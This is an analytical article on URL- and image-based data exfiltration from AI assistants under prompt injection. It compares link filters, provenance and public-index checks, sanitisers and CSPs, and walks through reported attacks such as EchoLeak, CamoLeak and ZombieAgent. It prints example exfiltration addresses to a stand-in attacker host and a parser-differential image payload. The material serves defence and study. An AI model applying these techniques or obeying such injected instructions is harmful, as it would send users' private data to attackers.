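- Ouyang and Narechania (2026), in *Analyzing the Presentation, Content, and Utilization of References*, asked 12 students to judge the accuracy of answers from nine assistants. ChatGPT had the highest rates, with about 22 per cent for hovering over references and 12 per cent for clicking them.
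- Pew Research Center analysed the browsing data of 900 American adults. According to Slashdot's *Google Users Are Less Likely To Click on Links*, they clicked on a source inside Google's AI summaries in 1 per cent of visits.

Deleting links can affect many readers even when the rate of checking per answer is low. In the experiment by Ding and colleagues, 83 of the 197 participants who saw citations (42.1 per cent) checked at least one. Checking was also associated with lower trust in the answer. Silently removing links therefore most affects readers who already doubt the answer and are most likely to catch a mistake.

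Ouyang and Narechania found that hovering was consistently more common than clicking, though with 12 students this is only a first indication. A reader who hovers may learn enough from the site's name or a preview. A defanged address still gives much of this information, as does a tooltip on a desktop computer. A visible address can also help readers spot a source that the model invented. One of Warren and colleagues' interviewees had received links to websites that didn't exist.

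Links also influence readers who never open them. Participants in Ding and colleagues' experiment trusted answers with citations more than answers without, even when the citations were random pages from other people's questions. They trusted answers with five citations no more than answers with one. If this holds for filtered answers, deleting the only link would make a correct answer look weaker, while deleting one of five would probably go unnoticed.

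But the effect may be small. Warren and colleagues showed 5,151 people screenshots of chatbot answers, some with source icons. People often rated the answers with icons no differently from answers without any indicator. Participants judged a prepared conversation and couldn't open the sources, which may explain part of the difference.

*Fostering Appropriate Reliance on Large Language Models* (2025) notes that sources may reduce overreliance if people open them, but may increase it if people just take them as a sign of credibility. A reader who would have trusted the link without opening it may therefore be better off without it. This is a weak argument for removing links silently, because the filter deletes them based on their address, whether or not the claim beside them is true.

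### What a visible marker should reveal

A marker ends the uncertainty about the missing source. Google also says that telling users about attacks it has stopped lets them watch out for similar ones. When Gemini withholds a summary because of suspicious content, it shows a warning banner with a link to a help page.

However, a marker can alarm or confuse people. If a filter wrongly rejects a link to `reports.example`, "suspicious link removed" casts doubt on a correct figure and the colleagues who published it. "[blocked]" doesn't suggest wrongdoing, but the manager could take it to mean that the site is down, the company's firewall blocked the link, or the whole answer is unreliable.

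When a filter replaces some links with a removal notice, readers might assume that someone has checked the links it leaves in place. Research on confidence labels suggests that this worry is reasonable, though a removal notice is a different kind of message. Warren and colleagues interviewed eight people, who disagreed about what a percentage under an answer meant. Some read it as the probability that the answer was correct, and others as the share of the answer that was accurate. One took high confidence to mean that the system had already verified the answer.

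A better-worded notice would probably help more than no notice. For example, "Image removed because its server is not on the approved list" gives the reason without claiming there was an attack.

Where the application puts the information may also matter. In *Seeing to Think?*, He and Liu (2026) had 372 people write short essays with an AI assistant that displayed its sources in different ways. Cards that appeared on hovering made it easy to check a source while working. When answers had many citations, people who saw the sources in a sidebar next to the text scored higher on critical thinking. None of the sources were defanged, but the result is a reason not to treat a tooltip and a visible address as equivalent.

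Printing the full address can also expose private data. The defanged chart address still ends in `?c=Anna%20Berg`. The manager may be allowed to see customer records, but the colleagues who receive the summary by email may not be. The application can leave out the path and query and show only the host, `img[.]attacker[.]example`. The host would still reveal the name if the attacker had put it in the subdomain, so the safest version shows only the registered domain, `attacker[.]example`. The manager can still report the server, and the full address stays in the log.

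## How does a system decide which links and images to neutralise?

An application needs a rule for deciding which addresses to defang, because defanging all of them would disable the manager's source link and defanging none would give away the customer's name. Blocking depends on the same rule, since an application has to recognise a dangerous address before it can withhold the answer containing it. Developers have used four criteria: the site an address belongs to, the site's reputation, where the address came from, and whether it was public before the conversation.

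### Four grounds and their errors

An allowlist names the permitted sites, or the permitted beginnings of addresses. With `https://reports.example/` on the list, the filter leaves the manager's link alone and neutralises the chart. An allowlist suits a company assistant that only cites one document store, but an assistant that searches the web would need a list of every site worth reading. If the developer forgets the final slash and the filter compares addresses as plain text, the entry `https://reports.example` also permits the attacker's site, `https://reports.example.attacker.example`.

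Even a correct list only identifies trusted sites, and attackers have used permitted sites that forwarded or stored data. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives redirects as one reason such a list isn't enough. The other is that strict lists cause frequent false alarms, which can train people to click through warnings.

The application can look up each address in a reputation service, which collects reports of malicious sites. Google checks links in Gemini's answers against its own service, Safe Browsing. The lookup works for sites the developer has never heard of, and it can catch a phishing page even if the model copied the link faithfully from an email. It is a poor guard against leaks because the attacker can register `attacker.example` on the day of the attack, before anyone has reported it, and the server only has to log requests. The lookup can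 also flag a safe site, such as a company's website that has recovered from a break-in but is still listed.

A URL provenance check records every address in the material that the model reads, and neutralises any address in the output that isn't in the record. Whoever hid the instructions in the quarterly report could write `https://img.attacker.example/chart.png?c=`, but didn't know the customer's name, so only the model could add `Anna%20Berg`. The finished chart address therefore won't be in the record. The link to the full report will be, provided the model copied it from that material. A phishing link that the model copies from an email also passes, because the check doesn't test whether a link is malicious.

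A system can also check links against an index of public addresses, for a similar reason. A crawler without access to the manager's conversation is unlikely to have recorded an address containing a private detail from it. This check doesn't require a record of what the model has read, but the index lacks pages the crawler couldn't reach, including internal reports, shared documents and anything published this morning.

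The table applies the four grounds to four addresses. The allowlist in this case contains `reports.example` and `calendar.example`.

| Address | Allowlist | Reputation service | Provenance | Public index |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `https://reports.example/q3`, copied from an internal report | Permits | Permits | Permits | Refuses |
| `https://img.attacker.example/chart.png?c=Anna%20Berg`, composed by the model under injection | Refuses | Permits until someone reports the server | Refuses | Refuses |
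| `https://calendar.example/new?title=Renewals%20meeting`, composed by the model at the manager's request | Permits | Permits | Refuses | Refuses |
| `https://attacker.example/a`, copied from the attacker's web page | Refuses | Permits until someone reports the server | Permits | Permits if the crawler has visited it |

The allowlist gets all four right, but only because the developer already knew both useful sites. The developer of an assistant that reads the open web has to choose among the methods in the other columns, and large products combine several of them.

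### Gemini's link check and markdown sanitiser

Google describes the treatment of addresses in Gemini's answers in *Mitigating URL-based Exfiltration in Gemini*, a post on its Bug Hunters site. Links go through a provenance check, while images and HTML get blunter treatment:

1. Google divides the sources of addresses into generative and non-generative ones. An address from a non-generative source, such as a search result, existed before the model wrote anything. A generative source is text that a model produced, so an injection may have shaped the addresses in it.
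2. The system checks each link in the answer against the provenance record.
3. The sanitiser removes all markdown images except those with data addresses. A data address begins with `data:` and contains the picture itself, so the browser has no server to contact.
4. The sanitiser escapes HTML.
5. Corrected addresses and well-known addresses are exceptions to the link check.

In the manager's answer, these rules would keep the link to the full report if its address came from the quarterly report. They would remove the chart, and would have removed a genuine one too. The logo sample is already text.

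It makes sense to treat images more strictly than links, because images load without a click and an answer can contain dozens of them. An attacker could put one image address for each letter of the alphabet into the quarterly report. Every address would pass a provenance check, and the model could then spell out a customer's name by displaying the images in order. A sanitiser that removes all external images prevents this.

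The exceptions are harder to assess. A model that copies a long address can get a character wrong, and an exact comparison would then refuse a good link. If the system replaces the faulty address with the recorded one, no new data can leave, but if it accepted small differences, an attacker could hide data in them. Exceptions for well-known addresses carry a similar risk. Opening the front page of an encyclopaedia reveals almost nothing about the user, but an exception for every address on the encyclopaedia's site would amount to an allowlist.

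Google can change these rules quickly. Gavish (2026), in *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*, lists URL sanitisation among the deterministic defences, which a central policy engine controls through configuration settings. Google can add a text pattern to catch a new attack faster than it can retrain a model. It also simulates attacks with and without a given defence to measure its effect, but Gavish gives no results for URL sanitisation.

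*The Trifecta*, a report by the security company Tenable, found parts of this design at work. Gemini redirected markdown links to a google.com address, truncated suspicious output, and sometimes refused to answer when it detected an injection. Tenable concluded that Gemini's tools were a more promising way to get data out than its answers, and one of the three vulnerabilities it reported was in the browsing tool. The link rules in Google's *How Gemini's defense-in-depth approach works* also restrict which addresses Gemini itself may open or pass information to.

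The image rule did not cover every product named Gemini either. SC Media reported on GeminiJack, an attack that Noma Labs found in Gemini Enterprise. Hidden instructions in an email, calendar invitation or shared document told Gemini to search for something like "emails from the sales department" and put the results at the end of an image address. Google had said in 2025 that this kind of leak was "not applicable to Gemini". Checkmarx, another security company, compares Gemini's sanitiser favourably with Microsoft Copilot Chat, but cites Google's own description of the sanitiser.

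### Copied addresses that the attacker wrote

Anthropic's assistant Claude opens web pages with a tool called `web_fetch`. Its requests can leak data just as a browser's can, even though nothing is displayed. The developer Simon Willison (2025) quoted the rule from Anthropic's documentation that Claude may not construct addresses, but may open those provided by the user or found in earlier search results or fetched pages.

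An injection might tell Claude to append the user's recent answers to an attacker's address and open the result. This fails even if Claude is fooled, because ordinary code, rather than Claude, compares the address with the conversation.

Willison saw a weakness in the phrase "URLs in user messages". Many applications paste emails or documents into the same message field as the user's own words, so an address in that field may come from an attacker. The documentation also permitted addresses from tools that the developer runs, which may also return untrusted text. Checking where an address came from is therefore only as reliable as the system's information about who wrote the text. Anthropic warned that some risk remained and offered developers a stricter setting that limits the tool to chosen domains.

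In July 2026 Willison (2026) described an attack by Ayush Paul on the Claude chat app, which can remember details from earlier conversations. The attack needed no composed address:

1. Paul set up a website that showed its hidden instructions only to visitors identifying themselves as Claude's fetching tool, which made the trap harder to spot.
2. The page claimed that AI assistants had to authenticate themselves by giving their user's name.
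3. It explained that, because of the limits of `web_fetch`, Claude would have to find the user's profile letter by letter. Below that it listed one link for each letter.
4. Claude opened the link for the first letter, and the server generated further links for the next step.

Claude had copied every address exactly from a page it had already fetched, so the rule permitted it. Paul's server recorded the order of the visits and obtained the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally, and paid no bounty. It fixed it by no longer letting `web_fetch` follow links from pages it had fetched, though Claude can still open pages that the user names or the search tool returns.

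The record correctly showed that the model had copied every address, all of which the attacker had written. The model chose only which address to open next, and those choices encoded the data.

### OpenAI's move to public addresses

OpenAI arrived at its present rule after several attempts. Rehberger reported the image leak in ChatGPT in April 2023. Microsoft, whose Bing Chat had the same flaw, restricted images with a CSP that May, but OpenAI did nothing until December. *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, a post on Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red, describes the check OpenAI then added. Before showing an image, the ChatGPT website sent the image's address to an OpenAI service called `url_safe`. If the service returned `{"safe":false}`, the website didn't load the image.

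OpenAI didn't publish the criteria, so Rehberger experimented. The service rejected an address that contained an email address in its query. He then created one image address for each letter and digit, and nine of the 36 passed. He couldn't find a reason why `a.png` passed and `d.png` didn't, but guessed that the service might be checking an index of existing pages. Using the addresses that passed, he got ChatGPT to send the word "hi" to his server in two requests. He suggested limiting the number of images in an answer.

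The website called the service, so every other ChatGPT app needed its own version of the check. The iPhone app didn't have one and remained vulnerable to the original attack. Rehberger reported further ways around `url_safe` in October 2024. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* showed that an attacker could by then take past conversations as well as the current one. OpenAI stopped those attacks around August 2025.

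OpenAI also used provenance to restrict which links ChatGPT's agents could open when they browsed pages and read email for the user. According to the news report *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, an attack called ShadowLeak had made ChatGPT build addresses out of private data. OpenAI responded by letting the agent open only addresses that it had received in exactly that form. The security company Radware then got around this rule with ZombieAgent, an attack whose injected email supplied a complete list of addresses, from `example.com/a` to `example.com/z` and from `example.com/0` to `example.com/9`, plus a token to stand for spaces. ChatGPT leaked the data one character at a time, much as Claude later did. According to the same report, OpenAI then let the agent open a link from an email only if a well-known public index contained it or the user had supplied it.

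OpenAI described the general form of this rule in January 2026, in a blog post by Adrian Spânu and Thomas Shadwell and in the paper *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. A crawler collects public addresses without access to conversations or accounts. Before ChatGPT automatically loads a page or image, the system checks whether that exact address is in the crawler's index. If it is, the page or image loads. If not, the system either tells the agent to try another website or warns the user that the link is unverified and may include information from the conversation. The user can then copy the link or open it anyway.

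The crawler must stay separate from the conversations. If the index also included addresses that users opened, a leaked address could enter it and count as public the next time. The test must also apply to the whole address, since `img.attacker.example` could easily have a public front page even if the address containing Anna Berg's name has never appeared anywhere.

OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* calls the mechanism Safe Url and adds that the user may see the information that would be sent. The mechanism covers, among other things, navigation in OpenAI's browser Atlas and both searches and navigation in Deep Research. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Rehberger writes that, as he understands it, an address typed by the user also counts as safe for the rest of the session. He considers the new rule a significant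 improvement but expects that some developers at OpenAI may not know about it and may leave it out of a new feature. A missing check had left the iPhone app vulnerable in 2023.

OpenAI's blog post doesn't report how many leaks the check stops or how many harmless links trigger the warning. The nearest outside measurement is in *The Framing Gap* (2026), which tested whether injected instructions could make a model send out a secret. A model accessed through OpenAI's API leaked the secret in up to 100 per cent of trials, depending on the attack, while ChatGPT leaked it in none of 48 valid trials. This is encouraging for ChatGPT as a product, but it doesn't show how much the address check contributed, because the researchers couldn't see inside ChatGPT and didn't attribute the result to any mechanism.

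### Legitimate addresses that look like attacks

The link to `calendar.example` in the table is the kind of thing people want from an assistant. So is a link to a map with the route already filled in, or to a support form that contains the order number. Each consists of a fixed beginning and a detail about the user, and so does the address in a leak:

```
https://calendar.example/new?title=Renewals%20meeting
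https://img.attacker.example/chart.png?c=Anna%20Berg
```

The provenance check and the public index check both reject the two addresses, and would do so even with a more complete record or a better crawler. The manager wants to send the meeting details to the calendar but doesn't want to tell a stranger about Anna Berg. Neither address contains the manager's wishes, so the system has to ask the manager or rely on a developer who decided in advance that `calendar.example` may receive meeting titles.

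OpenAI's warning takes the first route, which works best when the data is readable and warnings are rare enough that people still look at them. For links that an application needs often, the second route seems better to me than asking every time. The model can propose a title and a date, and ordinary code can put them into a fixed calendar address, so the worst an injection can do is create a silly meeting title.

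### What the choice of an address reveals

If the model may open any of *N* addresses whose requests the attacker can see, then, ignoring timing, the attacker learns at most log₂ *N* bits from one request and at most *k* log₂ *N* bits from a sequence of *k* requests. With 36 addresses, the limit is about 5.2 bits per request, enough to identify one letter or digit. With 4,096 addresses, it is 12 bits, so an attacker who already had a list of the company's 4,096 customers could assign an address to each and learn from a single request which one the manager was asking about.

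Even a single permitted address can leak the answer to a yes-or-no question, because the attacker can see whether the model opens it. A filter therefore can't eliminate the leak if it permits even one request to a server the attacker can observe. It can only reduce *N* and *k*, or make the requests easier to notice.

A public index limits *N* to the addresses a crawler has already recorded, though Rehberger says many larger websites probably have 36 suitable pages indexed. He also thinks an attacker could extend the vocabulary to thousands of addresses and teach the model the code through the injection. The index hinders nested links, like those in the Claude attack, more. A site that offers `/a`, then `/an`, `/ann` and finally `/anna` needs 456,976 addresses to cover every four-letter name alone, and the crawler must have recorded them before the attack.

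To reduce *k*, Rehberger suggests that the agent open each address only once per session, or reuse a stored copy for a few minutes. With one address per character, the name Anna Berg would then reach the attacker as "an berg", because the second *n* and the second *a* produce no new request. The attacker can get around this by supplying several addresses for each letter, or by using nested links, since every address in the sequence is new.

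Small leaks matter most when the secret is short. A few bits are of little use to an attacker who wants a whole customer database, but they can reveal a diagnosis, a vote on a takeover or whether a named person is a customer. For such cases, OpenAI now offers a stricter option called Lockdown Mode, which Willison reports limits the outbound requests themselves. OpenAI announced it in February 2026 and later extended it to personal accounts.

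## Why can rewritten output still leak data?

Rewritten output can still leak data when the filter misses a link, image or other element that can carry data, acts after the browser has already sent the request, allows requests to a server that passes data on, or cleans only part of an address. Blocking the whole answer would have prevented few of the leaks researchers have found in commercial products. A blocker also has to recognise the dangerous element, act in time and distinguish safe servers from unsafe ones, so it usually fails where a rewriter fails. Blocking has a clear advantage only over filters that clean an address and then let the browser use it.

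### Carriers that the filter doesn't recognise

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions from their emails, files and chats. In early 2025 it filtered links to outside websites out of its answers. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes how researchers at the security company Aim got around this. The filter recognised inline links and images but not reference-style ones, which put the address on a separate line at the end. It would have removed the inline chart from the sales manager's answer, but not a reference-style version of the same chart.

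The attack began with an email from outside the company. When an employee later asked Copilot a question, Copilot retrieved the email together with internal material and followed the email's instructions to put the most sensitive detail it could find into an image address. The employee didn't have to open the email or click anything. The researchers reported the flaw in January 2025 and Microsoft fixed it on its servers that May. According to Ravia, Microsoft confirmed that the flaw had affected no customers.

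A filter that rejected any answer in which it found an external link would still have delivered this one, because it would have found no link. EchoLeak also got past a Microsoft classifier meant to block injected instructions before they reached the model. The email never mentioned Copilot or AI and read like a request to a colleague, so the classifier let it through.

Ravia lists several ways of writing a reference-style link, and a filter that searches the raw text needs a rule for each. Filtering after the markdown parser has run is more reliable, because the parser turns every variant into the same `a` or `img` tag.

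Blocking a whole answer prevents leaks that rewriting would allow when the filter catches some of the links or images carrying data but misses others. Suppose an answer contains two images that each carry the customer's name, and the filter has a 90 per cent chance of recognising each one, independently of the other. Rewriting leaks the name if the filter misses at least one image, which happens in 1 − 0.9² = 19 per cent of cases. Blocking leaks it only if the filter misses both, which happens in 0.1² = 1 per cent of cases. Copilot's filter missed every reference-style link, so an attacker who used only those would have succeeded every time against either rewriting or blocking.

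*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) divides the attack into steps and marks which defences should stop each one. A dash means the defence doesn't apply to that step.

| Defence | Email makes Copilot use internal data | Email passes the classifier | Link passes the filter | Image loads by itself | Permitted server forwards the request | Data leaves without a click |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Labels that separate outside text from the user's request | Stops | Stops | – | – | – | Fails |
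| Internal sources only, unless the user asks for others | Stops | – | Stops | – | – | Fails |
| A limited set of markdown, or a fixed format | Stops | Stops | Stops | Fails | – | Fails |
| A list of permitted or forbidden addresses | – | – | Stops | Fails | Stops | Stops |
| A strict CSP | – | – | – | Stops | Stops | Stops |
| An image proxy with signed addresses that expire | – | – | – | Stops | Stops | Stops |
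| Human approval for outside content | Stops | Stops | Stops | Stops | – | Stops |
| Monitoring of outgoing data | – | – | – | – | – | Fails |

These marks are predictions. Reddy and Gujral state that they ran no experiments and worked only from public information, and the caption calls the table theoretical, although the paper's text refers to "our tests".

Several marks also depend on how strictly a developer applies the defence. Limited markdown is marked as failing against the self-loading image, and the subset that Reddy and Gujral recommend elsewhere in the paper does allow plain images. A subset without images would stop that step. EchoLeak got past Copilot's existing CSP, so the good marks for CSP can only apply to a much tighter policy. The marks for address lists are hard to explain, since they show the defence failing to stop the image from loading but stopping the data from leaving.

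### Filters that act too late

Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack on the search function of the same Microsoft product. The victim clicked a link to a Microsoft site, and Copilot treated part of the link's address as an instruction to search the victim's email. Copilot then wrote an `img` tag with the subject line of an email in the image's address. Subject lines sometimes contain login codes.

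Microsoft tried to neutralise HTML in Copilot's answers by wrapping them in a code block. But Copilot streams its answers, and it added the code block only after it had finished writing. By then the browser had rendered the image tag in the unfinished answer and requested the image. The finished page showed harmless text, so anyone who inspected it could have concluded that the defence had worked. Microsoft rated the flaw critical and has fixed it.

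Researchers had found a similar problem a year earlier in GitLab Duo, an assistant for programmers. Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft* reports that the first clue was a word whose formatting changed while the answer was still arriving. Duo converted the markdown line by line, before the structure of the whole answer was available, so some raw HTML became active. Instructions hidden in a public project could then make Duo send out source code from the user's private projects.

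Better timing alone wouldn't have protected GitLab Duo, because it sanitised its answers with DOMPurify, a widely used HTML sanitiser that mainly defends against scripts and keeps `img`, `form` and `a` tags by default. After Legit Security reported the problem in February 2025, GitLab stopped Duo from rendering tags such as `img` and `form` if they pointed outside `gitlab.com`.

Blocking at the same moment would also have failed in SearchLeak. Copilot could have replaced the finished answer with an error message, but the request had already been sent. A check that needs the complete answer protects the data only if the application holds back the whole answer until the check is finished, which is called buffering. Blocking requires buffering because the only image that justifies rejecting the answer may be in the last line.

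Suppose an assistant writes its first word after half a second, needs another 12 seconds to finish, and then spends half a second on the check. The manager can start reading after half a second with streaming, but sees an empty screen for 13 seconds with full buffering. Buffering delays the complete answer by only half a second, but most people notice the empty screen. pranav_pratik (2025) writes in *Real‑Time AI Streaming with Azure OpenAI and SignalR*, a Microsoft guide for developers, that waiting for a full answer "feels slow and breaks engagement".

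Cloud providers offer a compromise in which the application buffers the answer one piece at a time. AWS's *Configure streaming response behavior to filter content* describes a default mode that holds back one or more chunks until the content filter has scanned them. AWS says this adds "some latency" but gives no figure. Microsoft's Azure service also buffers and checks chunks by default, but it offers an asynchronous mode that shows text immediately while the filter runs. In that mode, a warning can arrive about 1,000 characters late. The chart in the manager's answer is only 65 characters of markdown, so the browser could have requested it long before the warning.

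These are general content filters, not link filters, but they have the same timing problem. Developers also have a reason to choose the weaker asynchronous mode, because it streams faster. AI SDK's troubleshooting page *Azure OpenAI Slow to Stream* repeats other users' advice to switch to that mode when answers arrive "slow and in big chunks". When Microsoft announced the mode, it warned that faster streaming could reduce safety.

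Rewriting needs much less buffering than blocking. When an image begins in the stream, the application can hold it back until its address is complete, decide what to do with it, and carry on, while the manager reads the paragraph about renewals. A reference-style image takes more care because its address may come at the end of the answer. Until then the parser treats the notation as ordinary text, and the filter has to check the image when the parser creates it. Varonis also recommends sanitising at render time rather than afterwards.

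An assistant can leak data through requests it makes before it starts to answer. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes several flaws in products of the email company Superhuman, including one in the assistant's web search, which could open any address. An email containing injected instructions could make the assistant add text from the inbox to an address on the attacker's server and then open it. Changing the displayed answer would not have prevented this leak, because the data had already been sent.

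### Permitted servers that pass data on

EchoLeak and SearchLeak both had to get past Copilot's content security policy (CSP), which permitted images only from certain servers. EchoLeak used a preview function in Microsoft Teams and SearchLeak used Bing's image search, both of which the policy permitted. Each service accepted a second address as part of the request and used its own servers to fetch it, so the browser's policy didn't apply. That second address contained the stolen data.

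Ravia published Copilot's list of permitted image servers in 2025, a year before Varonis published SearchLeak. Bing was one of its 29 different entries. The list also permitted everything under `sharepoint.com`, where Microsoft's customers, who may include an attacker, can have their own sites. The EchoLeak researchers first found a route through SharePoint, but it required the victim to accept an invitation to the attacker's site, so they looked for one that didn't.

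Reddy and Gujral recommend a CSP that permits only the application's own servers and uses no wildcards. That is good advice, but Microsoft owns both Teams and Bing, so "our own servers" could still have included them. Developers also need to check what each permitted server does with the addresses it receives. Varonis recommends reviewing every permitted domain that fetches addresses supplied by users. PromptArmor similarly advised the note-taking company Notion to make sure that nobody could use its image server to redirect requests past the CSP.

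A permitted server can also store the data for the attacker to collect. Superhuman's CSP allowed requests to `docs.google.com`, which hosts Google Forms. Anyone can create a form, and a form can accept a submission through a specially written address. The user only had to ask for a summary of recent mail. An email containing injected instructions then made the assistant write an image with such an address, which included other emails as the answer to the form's question. When the browser tried to load the image, it submitted the form. PromptArmor obtained the full text of several emails in one response, and parts of more than 40 emails in another.

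PromptArmor reported this on a Friday night in December 2025. Superhuman disabled the affected features the following Monday and deployed its first patch on Tuesday. PromptArmor published its account in January 2026, after Superhuman had fixed further problems. One of these was in Superhuman Go, another of the company's assistants, where the image could contact the attacker's server directly.

The Google Forms route appeared again in OpenAI's agent Codex. According to PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data*, an injected email could make Codex submit the user's other emails in the same way. PromptArmor reported the flaw in April 2026, and OpenAI has since fixed it. OpenAI had described its public-index check three months before the report. An address containing a private email shouldn't pass that check, so the check apparently didn't cover images in Codex. This fits Rehberger's prediction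 that some OpenAI developers would leave the check out of new features.

Sometimes a list of allowed domains includes one that is obviously unsafe. Willison pointed out that the browser tool in Antigravity, Google's programming assistant, was limited by default to a list of domains that included `webhook.site`, which records incoming requests and shows them to whoever set up the recording.

A redirect page can have the same weakness if it makes exceptions for trusted sites. Google's programming site Colab sends links in its assistant's answers through a Google page that asks the user to confirm, but Embrace The Red's *Google Colab AI* (2024) reports that this applied only to links outside Google. People can publish small programs at Google addresses through Google's Apps Script, and links to these programs opened without confirmation. In Rehberger's demonstration, one click sent the user's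 name, email address and notebook code to his script.

Google had already fixed a zero-click image leak in Colab that Rehberger reported in November 2023. At that time, the model had instructions not to display images, but he overrode them with a single prompt. An instruction to the model is weaker than a filter because the attacker's instructions reach the model too.

Data can leak even through a carefully designed image proxy, such as GitHub's Camo. GitHub Copilot Chat could display images only from GitHub's own servers, including Camo, which fetches outside images for project pages. Camo accepts an address only if GitHub has signed it with a secret key. A model can't produce the signature, so it can't add a customer's name to an address and have Camo fetch it.

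However, anyone can get GitHub to sign an address by publishing a page with an image in it. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how a researcher, Omer Mayraz, collected signed addresses in advance, one for each character, much like the list in the ZombieAgent attack on ChatGPT. Instructions hidden in a comment on a public project then made Copilot use these images to spell out the text he wanted, and Camo fetched them from his server. Each image was a single transparent pixel, so the user saw nothing unusual. Mayraz obtained the description of an undisclosed security flaw from a private project this way.

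The signature proved that GitHub had approved an address, but not for use in this answer. Expiring signatures, like those in the proxy in Reddy and Gujral's table, would have forced Mayraz to replace his collection of signed addresses now and then, but he could still have got new ones. The table's prediction for a signed proxy is therefore too optimistic unless the application also controls who can get an address signed.

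A cache might have hidden repeated letters from Mayraz, but Copilot could append a random number to a signed address without making it invalid, so every request looked new. A signature should cover the complete address, so that appending anything makes it invalid.

According to Legit Security, GitHub fixed the flaw by turning off all images in Copilot Chat, and reported it fixed as of 14 August 2025. SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories* reports that GitHub told Mayraz it had disallowed the use of Camo to leak user data. Both accounts can be true, because Copilot Chat can't send requests through Camo if it displays no images. The fix went further than GitHub's response to an earlier leak in Copilot Chat for the VS Code editor. Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat* reported in 2024 that GitHub had disabled markdown images from untrusted domains in that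 version.

Blocking wouldn't have prevented any of these leaks if the blocker had used the same list of trusted servers. It would have delivered the answer because the image came from Bing, Google or GitHub. Rejecting every answer with an image would have stopped the image leaks, but GitHub also stopped them by removing all images, and Copilot Chat's users still receive the text.

### Addresses that are only partly clean

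A filter can keep an address but try to remove the data from it. Reddy and Gujral advise stripping the query parameters, the part after the question mark, from permitted links. The table shows the effect on several addresses. The first three contain the customer's name in different places, and the last two are harmless.

| Original address | After stripping the query | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `https://attacker.example/chart.png?c=Anna%20Berg` | `https://attacker.example/chart.png` | The name is gone |
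| `https://attacker.example/anna-berg/chart.png` | Unchanged | The name leaks |
| `https://anna-berg.attacker.example/chart.png` | Unchanged | The name leaks |
| `https://calendar.example/new?title=Renewals%20meeting` | `https://calendar.example/new` | The calendar entry is blank |
| `https://reports.example/view?id=q3` | `https://reports.example/view` | The link no longer leads to the right report |

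Query stripping fails as a general defence because the attacker chooses where in the URL to put the data. In Reddy and Gujral's own description of EchoLeak, the secret is in the path. Even in the first row, the browser contacts the attacker's server, so the attacker learns that the model displayed the image.

Removing the query from link and image addresses works better if the filter already limits them to permitted servers, because it can stop leaks through those servers. In EchoLeak's Teams route and in SearchLeak, the attacker's whole address was in the query of a Microsoft address. Removing the query would have left Teams or Bing with nothing to fetch, even though the secret was in the path of the attacker's address. It would also have removed the stolen emails from the form submission in the Superhuman case.

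But a forwarding service can also take the destination from the path, as in `https://app.example/fetch/attacker.example/anna-berg`, and stripping the query doesn't change that. Stripping the query also wouldn't have stopped the attack through Camo, where the order of the images carried the data. An allowlist of exact server names stops data from leaking through the subdomain. To stop leaks through the path too, the filter has to check the complete address against known addresses.

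Stripping the query from a link can also do damage that nobody notices. A manager who sees "Full report [blocked]" knows the link was changed. If the link looks normal but opens the wrong report, the manager may think the assistant cited a bad source. A filter also has to strip queries before it adds a redirect page like Colab's, which carries the destination in its own query. Stripping queries afterwards breaks every link.

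Reddy and Gujral also suggest scanning the output for personal data and for long strings of random-looking characters, which may be encoded secrets. The second check could have caught the attack on GitLab Duo, which put encoded source code into the image address. It would be less useful at GitHub, because Camo's signatures look random by design, so the check would flag harmless images, and the leaked text never appeared in any address.

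If a filter recognises a suspicious address but cleans it badly, blocking the output instead would prevent the leak, provided the application hasn't displayed the address yet. Removing or defanging the whole address at that point would protect the customer's name equally well, and the manager would still get the figures.

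## What changes when another program renders the output?

An application that renders its own answers controls every step from the markdown to the browser's request. It loses that control when another program does the rendering, as happens when the sales manager tells the assistant to post the summary on a code-hosting site or email it to colleagues. The application can't add a CSP, a sandboxed frame or a confirmation dialog to the site or the mail program, so it can only change the text before sending it or refuse to send it. It also has to know what counts as a carrier at the destination, because text that does nothing in a chat window can load an image, notify a person or start a command elsewhere.

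### One string, two parsers

Renderers differ over more than bare addresses. The following line is harmless in one parser and loads an image in another:

```
<div markdown="1">![Renewals](https://img.attacker.example/a.png)</div>
```

Under CommonMark, a line that begins with `<div` starts an HTML block, and the parser leaves everything up to the next blank line unconverted. If the application permits raw HTML, a Markdown image on that line reaches the browser as text. The reader sees the exclamation mark, brackets and address, and the browser doesn't request the image.

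Showdown, a JavaScript converter with its own dialect of markdown, does convert the content of a `div` that has a `markdown` attribute. Its output is roughly this:

```html
<div markdown="1"><p><img src="https://img.attacker.example/a.png" alt="Renewals" /></p></div>
```

Now the browser loads the image. A filter that used a CommonMark parser to look for images would find none in this line and pass it to Showdown unchanged.

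CommonMark was an attempt to settle such differences, but they persist. It describes the HTML that should result from a given input, "which leaves many edge cases up for debate", according to the documentation of micromark, a parser that passes all of CommonMark's roughly 650 tests. Programs also add their own features, like Showdown's `markdown` attribute, which those tests don't cover.

Cleaning the final HTML avoids the problem because the filter runs after the markdown parser has interpreted the text. The image is an `img` tag in Showdown's output and text in the CommonMark output, and an HTML sanitiser handles both correctly regardless of which parser ran. The browser must still parse the cleaned HTML, but browsers share a detailed standard that covers even malformed HTML, so their results vary far less than those of markdown parsers.

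Vercel Labs' *Markdown sanitizers* describes two libraries. *harden-react-markdown* is for developers who render the markdown themselves, which Vercel Labs considers "easier to secure" because the developers control the whole process. *markdown-to-markdown-sanitizer* is for text that a third party such as GitHub or GitLab renders.

### Cleaning markdown for an unknown parser

The second library takes markdown and returns markdown, but it goes through HTML in between. Socket's *markdown-to-markdown-sanitizer*, a page in the security company's package directory, reproduces the documentation and lists the steps:

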